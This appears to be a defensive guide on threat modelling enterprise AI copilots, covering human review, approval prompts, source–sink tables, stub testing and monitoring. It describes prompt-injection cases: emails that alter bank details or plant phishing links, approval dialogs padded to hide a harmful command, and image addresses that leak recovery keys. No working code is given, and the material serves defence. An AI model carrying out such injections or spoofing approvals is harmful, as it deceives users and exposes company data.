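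## Can a person checking the output close the gap?

When software can't determine whether to carry out an outsider's request, most products ask the user. Users also check a copilot informally whenever they read an answer. Both checks depend on a person noticing that something is wrong. In recent experiments people seldom noticed, although better-designed screens helped considerably.

### False answers in the company's voice

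An answer can do damage even if no code runs and no data leaves the company. In 2024 Michael Bargury of the security company Zenity showed that an outsider's email could change the recipient of a bank transfer in Copilot's answer. Futurism reported that the employee didn't have to open the email. Many employees would be wary of new bank details in a stranger's email, but the same details look like company information when they come from the company's assistant.

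Harmful links can be disguised in the same way. In March 2026 the security company Permiso described an email that made Copilot add a false security alert, with a link, to an otherwise normal summary. According to eSecurity Planet's *AI Email Summaries Create a New Phishing Attack Surface*, Copilot in Teams was the version most likely to reproduce the attacker's text. Microsoft has fixed the flaw, and STAR Labs' *M365 Copilot* (2026) lists it as not exploited. Commercial steering, by contrast, is already common. Microsoft found more than 50 different prompts, from 31 companies, designed to plant recommendations in assistants' memories.

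A company can be held responsible for a false statement of policy even when no attacker is involved. Blanchard, Garvey and O'Laughlin (2026), in *Hallucinations in Organization-backed AI advisors*, cite a case in which a tribunal held Air Canada responsible for misleading information its chatbot gave a customer, even though the correct information was elsewhere on the airline's website. An attacker who can steer a copilot's answers about refunds or employee leave could cause the same kind of dispute deliberately.

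### How often people notice

The most direct test is *Are You Sure?* (Li, Dai and colleagues, 2026). The researchers compromised an assistant, then gave it to 303 people to use on realistic office tasks. In one task, a hidden note in a CV changed how the assistant ranked the candidates. Afterwards, the researchers asked participants whether anything had seemed unusual, and counted "unsure" as noticing.

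Among people who had seen only a disclaimer at the start, 8.6% noticed something wrong and 2.7% could describe the attack. The share who noticed was 20% with a reminder beside every answer and 25% with an alert that interrupted the task. The paper gives two conflicting sets of group sizes, so the differences between the warnings are less certain than the finding that few people noticed. Technical professionals did no better than anyone else.

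Alerts worked best where checking was easy. The interrupting alert raised the share of people who noticed the attack from 9.8% to 50% in a web search task, but only from 9.3% to 15% in an email task. Many people who saw an alert and still missed the attack trusted the assistant more afterwards, apparently because they took the alert as a sign that the product was carefully designed.

These participants had nothing at stake, and an accountant paying a real invoice might check more carefully. *AI advice suppresses people's willingness to say "I don't know"* (2026) offers some support for this, since rewarding accuracy made people rely on the AI less. But across its five experiments, access to advice that was usually wrong nearly eliminated people's willingness to admit they didn't know.

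How sure people are of their own answer also affects whether they accept a wrong one. In *Do People Trust AI Assistants Even When They Are Consistently Wrong?* (2026), a consistently wrong assistant persuaded people 61% of the time when they were unsure, and 21% of the time when they were very confident and had feedback showing that the assistant was wrong. People mostly ask a copilot about things they don't already know, so they will often be unsure when they check its output.

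### Citations help only if someone opens the right source

Citations make an answer easier to check. In the studies that Blanchard and colleagues reviewed, citing sources reduced people's reliance on wrong answers, while explanations without sources could increase it. General warnings that the AI can make mistakes had weak and mixed effects. Few of these studies looked at assistants that speak for an organisation, so the results may not apply exactly to a company copilot.

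Many users never open the sources. For *Analyzing the Presentation, Content, and Utilization of References*, Ouyang and Narechania (2026) watched 12 students use nine chatbots. Even on the chatbot with the most engagement, students hovered over about 22% of references and clicked about 12%. The sample is tiny. A larger worry is that citations raised people's trust in an answer even when researchers had picked them at random, as Ding, Facciani and colleagues (2025) found in *Citations and Trust in LLM Generated Answers*. Trust was lower among people who checked the citations.

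An attacker can also interfere with the citations, because the model usually selects them. The EchoLeak email, for instance, got Copilot to leave it out of the sources. In another of Bargury's demonstrations, described in Willison's *living off microsoft copilot*, Copilot displayed the attacker's information beside a reference to the wrong document. An employee who clicked the reference would have found a genuine document, and might not have checked whether it contained the figure.

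The copilot's software assembled the context, so it has a better record than the model of what the context contains. It can show a list of every outside text in the context, whether or not the model cited it. Microsoft recommends signals like this when untrusted data influences an output. The list may be long, so it makes sense to put outside emails and web pages first.

A list of sources is probably too weak a safeguard for the facts an attacker would most like to change. If an answer mentions a supplier's bank account, the software can fetch the account number from the company's payment records and display it in a box that the model can't write to. The employee then sees the right number without having to suspect anything.

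### What an approval prompt has to get right

An approval prompt pauses the copilot before a consequential action and asks the user to allow it. Microsoft calls this "the last line of defense" and lists it after nine other measures. Google calls it a "final safeguard" against a successful injection.

Asking Ann makes sense because only she knows whether she wanted a password reset. But her answer is useful only if she sees the real action, understands its effect, knows which untrusted text was involved, and gets few enough requests to read each one.

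The first of these conditions failed in Lies-in-the-Loop, an attack that the security company Checkmarx described in *Bypassing AI Agent Defenses With Lies-In-The-Loop* (September 2025). A developer asked Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, to deal with a public issue that a stranger had written. The issue made the agent request permission for a harmful command and add long, reassuring text after it, which pushed the command off the top of the window. Every developer who tried it approved the request, though Checkmarx doesn't say how many there were.

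Anthropic replied that this was outside its threat model, because users are responsible for reading the whole prompt, including scrolling up. A follow-up, Checkmarx's *Turning AI Safeguards Into Weapons with HITL Dialog Forging*, showed that an attacker could also influence the one-line summary attached to the request. A developer could therefore read the summary, skim the visible text and approve the request without knowing what would run.

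The remedy is to have a separate component, rather than the agent, build the approval request from the action that is about to run. Weng (2026), in *What You Approve Is What Executes*, borrows this idea from cryptocurrency hardware wallets, which display a payment on their own screen because malware may control the computer. The approval is valid only for the exact action in the request, so it no longer applies if the agent changes the recipient afterwards.

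This is difficult for coding agents, because it can be hard to tell from a shell command what it will do. Weng's prototype let through 10% of 1,330 known abuses of ordinary tools without prompting the user. It also marked 87% of 28,798 normal commands as impossible to inspect, which would prompt the user far too often. This is easier for an office copilot with narrow tools. If the tool call is a password reset for E10482, ordinary code can look up the name and display "Reset the password of Ann Lee".

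### Seeing the action isn't the same as understanding it

An accurate request can still mislead. Suppose a user asks an agent to send only summary totals to an auditor, and a hostile note makes the agent copy the raw invoice rows into the report. The agent then asks for approval to send the report to the auditor. The tool, recipient and file name are all correct, but the request doesn't show what the file contains.

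*When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) compared four approval screens using cases like this one. Eighty unpaid volunteers made 12 decisions each, and half of the requests were unsafe.

| What the screen showed | Unsafe requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 seconds |
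| The exact tool arguments | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 seconds |
| Arguments, the user's original restriction and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 seconds |
| The same facts, with the combined consequence stated | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 seconds |

Most of the improvement came from giving people more facts. Stating the consequence (for example, that the attachment was built from raw invoice rows) probably helped too, but the study was too small to be sure. After adjustment, its estimated effect ranged from 19.7 percentage points fewer unsafe approvals to 3.8 more. When the violation depended on several linked steps, the last two screens did equally badly, each with 7 unsafe approvals out of 30.

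Even with the best screen, about a quarter of the unsafe requests got through, in a test where half the requests were unsafe. That screen also took twice as long as the short description, which matters if requests keep coming.

There is less evidence on whether naming the untrusted text helps. Approval requests in Microsoft's version of FIDES name the tool and the label that caused the block, though Microsoft admits the requests are still coarse. Hossain and colleagues added the log and the user's restriction at the same time, so their results don't show what each contributed. Naming the source still seems worth doing, since "this address came from an email you received today" gives Ann something she can check.

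### Approval fatigue

People who get many approval requests stop reading them. *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (Anthropic, 2026) reports that users approve 97% of permission prompts. Most of the commands are safe, so the approval rate alone doesn't show that users are careless. A controlled study in the same article provides much stronger evidence.

Anthropic had 1,053 paid testers do coding work, and during each session it replaced the text of one prompt with a clearly dangerous command. The testers rejected the command 13.6% of the time. Their rejection rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. An automated classifier that reviews each action blocked 89% of the same commands.

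Adding a person as a last check behind the classifier would have raised the number of commands caught from 937 to only 943. The classifier missed 116 commands, and the testers caught 6 of those, or about 5%, so the rest evidently looked ordinary to people as well.

Anthropic has an interest in this result, since it sells an agent that is more useful when it runs without interruption. The testers worked in a test environment, not on their own projects, so they had less to lose. Weng also cites an independent test in which the classifier missed a substantial share of risky actions. Still, 13.6% is so low that Anthropic's earlier advice to read every prompt carefully looks unrealistic.

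Smaller studies found similar results. Of 16 participants in *Options, Not Clicks* (2026), only 3 said they read permission prompts carefully, and 13 used "Always Allow" just to get rid of them. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analysed 290 reports of agents damaging files and found that user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 of those 105, the user had switched on automatic approval.

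Nearly all the recent evidence comes from coding agents or short experiments. Hossain and colleagues fall back on research from 2010 and 2013 about consent dialogs and browser warnings for what happens over months when attacks are very rare. That research found that people accept familiar-looking dialogs out of habit, but that a warning's design makes a large difference. An office worker who sees two well-designed requests a week might do far better than a developer who sees fifty in an afternoon, but nobody seems to have measured this.

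### When to ask, and what to show

Microsoft's case for approval still holds after this evidence, but in a narrower form. Microsoft recommends approval for high-risk or irreversible actions, alongside other controls. When those controls have already made attacks rare, a person who catches one attack in seven, or even three in four, is a useful addition. But it would be reckless to give a copilot a dangerous tool just because somebody will check.

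The team's first job is therefore to remove approval requests that don't need a person. The helpdesk copilot can search the wiki or open a ticket without asking, because the worst outcome of either is tolerable. For coding agents, sandboxing cut permission prompts by 84%, according to an Anthropic figure cited in *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026).

Users may also review a whole plan more carefully than individual steps. Anthropic found that users rejected 39% of the plans Claude Code proposed, compared with 3% of individual permission requests. Many of those users may have just wanted a different approach, but they were reading the plans. Approving a plan is safe only if the software then stops the copilot from deviating from it, as CaMeL's interpreter does.

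The system shouldn't ask anyone to approve an action that should never happen. If the helpdesk copilot tries to send a recovery key outside the company, ordinary code should block it without giving Ann the option to approve it, because an attacker could trick her into doing so.

That leaves actions that are irreversible or that send something out of the company, and that Ann might really want. When she asks the copilot to send her laptop's warranty document to a repair firm, the screen might show:

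- **Your request:** "Send the repair firm my warranty document", exactly as she typed it
- **Action:** send one email with one attachment
- **Recipient:** the full address, with a note that it came from an outside email and isn't in the company's supplier list
- **Attachment:** the warranty document, with a link to open it

Ordinary code should fill in every line of the approval screen from the tool call and the company's records. If the screen has to include text that the model wrote, such as the body of the email, that text should appear below the facts in a marked box of limited size, with formatting switched off. The software should send exactly what Ann approved, and ask for approval again if anything changes.

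A person's refusal also has to stop the action. One developer interviewed for *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) refused several requests, but the agent kept trying other ways to do the same thing. If Ann refuses to send the document, the software should block outgoing messages for the rest of the chat, so that the copilot can't keep making slightly different requests until she approves one.

For a few actions, one person's approval isn't enough, however well the screen is designed. A change to a supplier's bank details should go to a second employee, who makes the usual check with the supplier. The second employee shouldn't rely on the copilot's summary, because a hostile email that prompted the change may also have shaped the summary.

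## How does a team build the threat model, step by step?

Each control described so far blocks one way a copilot's output can do harm. A team builds a threat model to find out which of those ways exist in its own copilot and which to block first. Microsoft suggests starting by mapping where untrusted data enters, defining what the system must never do, and planning detection and response. The example below goes beyond these steps and models the helpdesk copilot as its team might first have built it, with a chat panel that loads outside images and a reset tool that is always available.

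### What to protect and what must never happen

Microsoft advises teams to start with assets, not attacks. That seems right, because a team that starts with attacks will mostly list the ones it has read about. The helpdesk team might list:

- staff accounts, which a password reset can open or lock
- the recovery keys in the asset database
- the contents of staff mail and tickets
- the tickets themselves, which people and other copilots rely on
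- the correctness of answers, including the helpdesk's own phone number

Microsoft says teams often under-protect abstract assets like trust and correctness, although failures there do the most lasting damage. For example, an attacker who can change the phone number in the copilot's answers will get calls from employees who are ready to follow instructions.

The team then writes down what the copilot must never do:

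1. Start a password reset that the account's owner or an administrator didn't request with a button outside the chat.
2. Show or send a recovery key to anyone who isn't entitled to it.
3. Send text from mail, tickets or the database outside the company, unless a person has approved that exact message.
4. Cause text that the model wrote to run as code.

A tester should be able to check each limit and get a yes or a no. "Protect personal data" is too vague for that.

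Microsoft also suggests asking who the adversary is, what they want, and how the system could help them. The helpdesk team has at least two adversaries: an outsider who wants data or an account, and a temporary worker who wants an administrator's permissions. The team should also plan for accidents, such as employees using the copilot for a job it wasn't designed for. For example, Ann might ask it whether a suspicious email is genuine, which would put the email in the copilot's context while it wrote the answer.

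### Draw the system as it runs

Design documents usually describe a simpler system than the one running. Microsoft therefore tells teams to model how the system actually operates. It also says that AI systems are more likely to fail in the gaps between components than at their most obvious boundaries. Teams can find these gaps by sending one request through a test system and following it through every log.

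The helpdesk team might discover this way that the ticket system emails each new VPN ticket to a list of contacts that includes the VPN supplier. They might also discover that the security team reads the copilot's logs in a viewer that displays formatted text. The copilot's developers didn't build the email feature or the log viewer, so their design didn't include them.

The corrected drawing might look like this:

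```
employee's question --+           +--> chat panel ------> employee
staff mail -----------+           +--> asset database
tickets --------------+--> MODEL -+--> ticket system ---> email notices
wiki -----------------+           +--> reset system
asset database -------+           +--> log -------------> log viewer
```

The team draws a trust boundary all the way around the model, as if an unknown outsider were running it. This means instructions in the system prompt don't count as controls, because the model might not follow them. The team has to put its checks in ordinary code that runs after the output leaves the model.

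### List the sources and sinks

The team records who can write to each source, using the same levels as before. Mail and tickets are level 0, and the wiki, the asset database and Ann's question are level 1.

To keep the table small, the team can group sources that have similar authors and readers. Three groups are enough here: emails from outsiders, tickets from outsiders, and wiki pages that a colleague has altered. Emails and tickets stay separate because an email usually enters the copilot of the employee who received it, while a ticket enters the copilot of an administrator like Ben.

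Sinks are easier to miss because many of them are behind another system. For each sink, the team should ask what reads the text next, and keep asking until nothing else reads it. This leads from the ticket system to the email notices, and from the log to the viewer and the administrator using it. The team should mark every sink that is also a source, such as the ticket system.

### Fill in the table

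For each combination of source and sink, the team asks what would happen if an attacker wrote the copilot's output. It doesn't yet ask how likely that is, or how the attacker would manage it.

| Sink | Outsider's email, in Ann's copilot | Outsider's ticket, in administrator Ben's copilot | Altered wiki page, in anyone's copilot |
|---|---|---|---|
| Chat panel | An image address carries Ann's recovery key to an outside server | An image address carries any employee's recovery key out | Everyone who asks about the VPN may leak something |
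| Asset database | A query reads Ann's device records | A query reads every device record | Queries read whatever each user may read |
| Ticket system | A new ticket quotes Ann's mail, and the notice sends it to the supplier | A new ticket quotes a confidential ticket, and the notice sends it out | Hostile text spreads into new tickets |
| Reset system | Ann is locked out, or loses her account if the copilot can read the reset message | An attacker can target any account, including the chief executive's | Many employees are locked out on the same morning |
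| Log viewer | A script runs in the browser of whoever reads the log | The same | The same, from many chats |
| Person reading the answer | Ann calls a false helpdesk number | Ben turns off a security setting | Staff install a fake VPN update |

The ticket column is the worst, even though most public demonstrations have used email, because Ben's copilot works with Ben's permissions.

The database row looks harmless alone because a query only brings data into the context, but it becomes serious when another sink can carry that data out. After filling in the cells, the team should therefore return to each mild one and ask what a later output could do with the result. The team should also go through the table again, assuming a model error instead of an attacker. The model could mistakenly quote Ann's mail in a ticket without any hostile text, and the notice would still go to the supplier.

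### Rank the cells by impact

Security teams have traditionally ranked risks by multiplying impact by likelihood. Microsoft says this doesn't work for systems that run at massive scale, where something that happens once in a million interactions may happen thousands of times a day. With two billion interactions a day, for example:

**2,000,000,000 × 1/1,000,000 = 2,000 times a day**

Microsoft uses impact to set the priority and likelihood to shape the response. A severe failure gets attention however rare it is. People can handle each case if such failures are rare, but the team needs automatic controls if they are frequent, because nobody could review that many cases by hand. Microsoft adds that "low likelihood" is never a reason to leave a threat without a response plan.

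The expected number of failures is less alarming for one company. If staff ask the helpdesk copilot 5,000 questions a day, a one-in-a-million fault will appear about once every 200 days. It is still a mistake to look only at the small rate, because the 2,000 failures become apparent only when the rate is multiplied by the number of interactions.

A better reason for the helpdesk team to rank by impact is that attackers will reuse whatever works. The failure rate in ordinary use is therefore a poor guide to how often the failures in the worst cells will occur.

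Public incidents don't give a reliable likelihood either. Intrinsec's *Enterprise LLM Threat Atlas* collects 36 public cases across 12 threat scenarios. It has five research cases and no real incidents for improper output handling, and three of each for the abuse of tools and agents. Intrinsec takes the overall distribution as a hint about where the greatest risks are. But victims may never notice a leak through an image address, so the lack of reported incidents is weak evidence that leaks are rare.

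Some scoring systems mix impact and likelihood without making it obvious. Huang and colleagues gave tool poisoning 46.5 out of 50 using DREAD, which scores a threat on damage, reproducibility, exploitability, affected users and discoverability. Three of the five scores are about how easy the attack is, so an easy attack that does little damage can outrank a serious one. For example, if a takeover of the chief executive's account gets 10 for damage and 4 for everything else, it totals 26, while a misfiled ticket with 3 for damage and 8 for everything else totals 35.

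Three severity levels are probably enough for the helpdesk. A cell is severe if its outcome would break one of the "never" limits, serious if it would cause harm that takes real work to undo, and minor otherwise. Every cell in the reset row is severe, as is any cell in which a recovery key or someone's mail leaks.

Likelihood then determines how the team responds. If a ticket ever leads the copilot to try to reset someone else's account, an alert should go to a person at once. The chat panel will often block outside images because many harmless emails contain logos, so the software can do this automatically and just keep a count.

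### Choose controls and name an owner

For each severe cell, the team picks at least one deterministic control and records what could still go wrong. It can do the same for serious cells, such as a false phone number. Part of the record might look like this:

| Cell | Control | Remaining risk | Owner |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ticket to reset system | Removal of the reset tool once outside text enters the chat, and a trust-level check in the reset system | A developer labels a new source wrongly | Head of the identity team |
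| Email to reset system | The same, plus a reset button outside the chat | A false answer persuades Ann to press the button | Head of the identity team |
| Ticket to chat panel | Images only from the application, and links built from document numbers | A new output format opens another route | Product manager for the copilot |
| Email to ticket system | No outside notices for tickets the copilot wrote | A technician forwards the ticket by hand | Helpdesk manager |
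| Any source to log viewer | Plain text only in the viewer | Someone exports the log to a tool that formats it | Head of security monitoring |
| Email to person | Phone number and download links from company records, in a box the model can't write to | Ann follows false advice elsewhere in the answer | Helpdesk manager |

The risk owner should be someone who would have to deal with the damage and has the authority to switch the feature off. A developer usually has neither that responsibility nor that authority. David C says the people who own the risk need to know that some of it will remain. The owner's signature means little if they believe a filter has solved the problem.

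Controls also have drawbacks. Microsoft's *Complete AI threat modeling* lists extra complexity, slower responses, and the work of logging and review. For a minor cell, the team may reasonably decide that a control's drawbacks outweigh the harm. If a severe cell has no acceptable control, Microsoft advises rethinking the feature. For instance, the helpdesk could stop the copilot from reading recovery keys and leave them on a separate page with its own login.

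### Check the table against published frameworks

Published frameworks are most useful once the team has its own table, because the team can then use them to find what it left out. STRIDE is a long-established list of six kinds of threat: spoofing (pretending to be someone else), tampering, repudiation (being able to deny an action), information disclosure, denial of service, and elevation of privilege. Huang and colleagues applied STRIDE to assistants that use MCP and identified 57 threats across five components.

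The helpdesk team can go through the six STRIDE categories for each sink. For the ticket system, they can ask under repudiation whether anyone could prove that Ann didn't write a ticket the copilot filed under her name. Under denial of service, they can ask whether a hostile email could make the copilot fill the queue with junk. Neither problem is in the table above. But none of the six categories covers whether an answer is true, so a team that used only STRIDE could easily overlook the false phone number.

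OWASP's list of risks for LLM applications has an entry for improper output handling, but it covers only part of the harm that output can do. SC Media's *OWASP updates top 10 security risks for LLM applications* lists sensitive information disclosure second, excessive agency third and misinformation seventh. A team needs all four entries to build the helpdesk table, and would miss most of the rows if it read only the entry on output handling.

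OWASP's separate list for agentic applications adds failures that can develop over several steps. TechRepublic's *OWASP Drops First AI Agent Risk List* describes the list's first entry as malicious content that changes an agent's objectives, and the second as the misuse of legitimate tools. According to Giskard (2025), later entries include unexpected code execution, memory poisoning, cascading failures and exploiting people's trust in agents. None of the ten titles is about displaying an answer or fetching a link.

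MITRE ATLAS catalogues the techniques attackers use against AI systems and gives security teams shared names for alerts and incident reports. Intrinsec maps improper output handling to a single ATLAS technique, LLM Response Rendering. For output that runs as a command or makes a server send a request, it uses ATT&CK, MITRE's older catalogue of ordinary intrusions. A team that searched only ATLAS for output problems might therefore consider only the chat panel and overlook these cases.

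ETSI, a European standards body, published *Baseline Cyber Security Requirements for AI Models and Systems* as TS 104 223 in April 2025. Infosecurity Magazine's *ETSI Unveils New Baseline Requirements for Securing AI* reports that the specification has 13 core principles, which expand to 72 trackable items across five phases, from secure design to end of life. In December 2025, ETSI issued EN 304 223, a European Standard on the same subject. Help Net Security's *A new European standard outlines security requirements for AI* lists indirect prompt injection among the risks the standard addresses.

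| Framework | What it adds | Gap on output |
|---|---|---|
| STRIDE | Six questions to ask about any sink | No question about whether an answer is true |
| OWASP list for LLM applications | A named entry for output handling, with defences | Spreads the harm from output over several entries |
| OWASP list for agentic applications | Tools, identity, memory and chains of agents | No title about display or automatic fetching |
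| MITRE ATLAS | Shared names for attackers' techniques | One main technique for output, with ATT&CK needed for the rest |
| ETSI TS 104 223 | Duties across the system's whole life | Organised by life-cycle phase, so the team must work out each sink itself |

A small team doesn't need all five. STRIDE and the two OWASP lists cover most of what the helpdesk has to decide before launch. ATLAS becomes useful when the security team writes alerts, and the ETSI standard when a customer or auditor wants evidence of a process. ETSI's last phase is also a reminder to decide who will cancel the copilot's permissions when the company retires it.

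### Test with a hostile model

The team now has controls that should work even if an attacker manipulates the model. These are hard to test with the real model, because a good model may not produce the harmful output that the controls are meant to stop. The team can instead run a hostile-model test, which replaces the model with a stub, a small program that returns whatever the tester has written. The rest of the system runs as usual.

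Ma and colleagues used this approach to check repairs to open-source software. They replayed prepared malicious outputs instead of calling a live model, because they wanted to know whether the code downstream was safe once a bad output existed. The same method suits a company's own copilot:

1. The team sets up a copy of the system with invented employees, passwords and recovery keys.
2. It puts an outsider's email or ticket into the context through the normal route, so that the real code sets the trust labels.
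3. For each severe cell, the stub returns the worst output the tester can write.
4. The tester checks the sink itself to see whether the password changed, the query ran, or a request reached the team's test server.
5. The tester repeats the process with ordinary outputs, to make sure that the copilot still works.

For the helpdesk, the worst outputs would include a call to the reset tool after the software has removed it, a reset of Ben's account from Ann's chat, and an answer with an invented recovery key in an image address. The stub should also be able to use what a tool returns, because a real model could look up a key in one step and put it in a ticket in the next. A stub with only fixed answers could not reproduce that sequence.

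Each cell needs more than one hostile output. Ma and colleagues wrote several variants of each attack, and used 429 security tests and 411 function tests for 116 vulnerabilities. Depending on the repair tool, between 27% and 44% of failed repairs kept the software's normal functions but left at least one attack working. Another 11% to 25% blocked the attacks but broke something useful. The team also needs ordinary tests, because a reset system that refuses every request would pass all the hostile ones.

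In red-teaming, people or programs attack the complete system with its real model. If the model resists every attack, the red team learns nothing about the reset system's own checks. The hostile-model test shows whether those checks hold no matter how an attacker fools the model, and the result stays valid when the supplier releases a new model. The test is also fast and repeatable, so developers can run it after every code change.

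Unlike a stub, red-teaming can estimate how often attackers succeed and test whether hostile text gets past the classifier and into the context. It can also produce outputs that no tester would have thought to write. Ma and colleagues acknowledge that their prepared variants can't cover everything a model might produce. A stub also doesn't show whether Ann would believe a false phone number. A team that can use both methods should add every successful output from the red team to the stub's collection.

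### Trace output through the code

A hostile-model test covers only the sinks the team knows about. Static analysis, which examines code without running it, can find others. One form, taint analysis, marks data as untrusted where it enters a program and follows it to functions that could do damage, such as those that run commands.

Ordinary taint analysis tends to stop tracking untrusted data once it passes through a model. *Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary* (Xu, Cheng and colleagues, 2026) explains that the widely used tools CodeQL and Semgrep don't treat a model's reply as a source of untrusted data. GitHub's *CodeQL 2.26.0 adds Kotlin 2.4.0 support and AI prompt injection detection* (2026) may give a team the wrong impression, because the new query finds user input that flows into a system prompt and doesn't track the model's output. Some commercial tools do cover output. Snyk's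 product reports untrusted data from a model when it reaches a sensitive function, according to Cupovic's *Snyk Code Improvements*.

*TaintP2X*, by He, Wang and colleagues, presents a research tool that traces a model's replies through an application's code. The tool recognises 97 standard ways of calling a model, uses a language model to find developers' own variations on them, and checks whether the replies reach any of 236 dangerous functions. It found 27 of 35 known vulnerabilities. In a scan of 4,772 open-source projects, it reported 101 paths from a reply to a dangerous function, spread across 75 projects. Developers had confirmed seven vulnerabilities and fixed five by the time of publication.

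False alarms are the main difficulty. In one comparison, tracing alone flagged 263 paths, of which 168 were false alarms. TaintP2X then used a language model to discard paths that looked safe, which reduced the false alarms to 36 but also reduced the correctly flagged paths from 95 to 78. For a single copilot, it may be better to skip this filtering and have a developer look at every path, since there won't be many.

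Xu and colleagues also reduce false alarms, by classifying how each piece of a prompt usually affects the reply. Some pieces are copied word for word, some are reduced to a score, and some leave no trace. On a measure that combines false alarms with missed flows, their method scored 81.7%, compared with 47.5% for treating every piece as reaching the output. But the categories come from ordinary inputs. An attacker might write text that the model copies in full where it would normally return only a score, so a team should be careful about marking a dangerous path as safe on this basis.

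Tracing is strongest for code execution, which made up 74 of TaintP2X's 101 paths, while none involved displaying output in a page. Tracing also can't follow text into another company's service, or find a ticket notice that an administrator set up in a settings menu.

### Monitor, respond and review

Before anything goes wrong, the team has to decide what to log. David C suggests logging enough to identify suspicious activity, which may mean the model's full input and output and its tool calls. Intrinsec is more cautious about raw text and recommends recording details such as document numbers, sensitivity labels, tool names and authorisation decisions. That caution is justified because logs can leak. Intrinsec cites a chat app whose misconfigured database reportedly exposed about 300 million messages from 25 million users.

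The helpdesk team can do both. It can keep the details in its main log and the full text in a separate store that few people can open, and delete the text after a fixed period.

Deterministic controls provide a better signal than a search for typical injection phrases, because a blocked action is a clear event. If the copilot calls the reset tool after the software has removed it, the cause is either a bug or an attack, and both are worth investigating. Intrinsec also recommends alerts for suspicious sequences, such as a copilot that retrieves sensitive documents, summarises them, then shares something outside the company. One of Microsoft's measures of success is that the team learns of misuse from its own monitoring rather than mainly from users' reports.

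The response should be ready in advance. The team needs a switch for each tool and each source, so that it can turn off resets without shutting down the whole copilot. If it suspects an injection, it might:

1. turn off the affected tools and cancel the copilot's access tokens
2. find the chat and every text in its context
3. remove the hostile text and rebuild the search index, so that no copilot retrieves it again
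4. find every other chat that included the same text
5. check everything those chats wrote or sent, including tickets

The last two steps are easy to skip. If the hostile email went to 300 employees, Ann's chat is only the first one anybody noticed. A ticket her copilot wrote may also still contain the attacker's text.

The team should also review the threat model whenever the system changes. A new source adds a column to the table, and a new sink adds a row. A web search tool adds both, because its results enter the context and its search terms leave the company. It would increase the helpdesk table from 18 cells to 28. Changing the copilot's model adds no cells, but it makes the red team's results out of date. Other reasons for a review are a new group of users with more permissions, a new output format, and a published attack on a similar product. The team should also set a date for the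 next review, in case a supplier changes something without announcing it.

### When the company buys the copilot

Most of this assumes that the team can change the software. Intrinsec distinguishes copilots that a company runs itself from those built into a supplier's product, where the customer controls only the settings, access to data, and governance. That customer can't replace the model with a stub, trace the output through the code, or add a check before a tool call.

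It can still fill in the table, because it knows who can write to its mail and files and can learn from the documentation what the product can do. Only the controls column changes, and it now has four kinds of entry.

**Settings** come first. The company can turn off connectors, add-ons and output formats that staff don't need, and restrict who may install third-party apps. Each one it turns off removes a row or a column from the threat model.

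Permissions matter more for a copilot bought from a vendor than for one the company builds, because the company may have no other way to limit what an attack can reach.

**Logs** are useful only if the supplier records the right events. Intrinsec suggests comparing use of the AI features with bulk access to documents, new external sharing links, and new permissions that users grant to apps. When something looks wrong, the company can turn off the AI features for the people affected, revoke the app permissions and review the sharing links. Before buying a copilot, the company should check whether the log identifies the documents the copilot read and whether it can export those records.

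The fourth entry is the **supplier's speed in fixing flaws**, over which the customer has little influence. Microsoft took between about seven and 16 weeks to fix the ReLeak flaws, and customers could do little in that time because they hadn't heard of them. A company can ask how quickly the supplier has fixed serious flaws in the past, whether it tells customers afterwards, and which features customers can turn off themselves. The last answer may be the most valuable, since customers can turn off a feature the day a flaw becomes public, before the supplier has fixed it.

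The company can also run a rough version of the hostile-model test, but should first check the supplier's rules on security testing. In a test account with invented data, an employee asks the copilot for an answer that contains an image from the company's own test server. If the server receives a request for the image, that route is open. If the copilot refuses, the route may still be open, because an attacker might find a way to get it to comply.

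For some severe cells, the customer may have no control to apply. The customer then has to either keep the data or the tool away from the copilot, or have the risk's owner accept in writing that the supplier's defences are the only protection. For a password reset, leaving the tool switched off and giving staff a link to the reset page would be easier.
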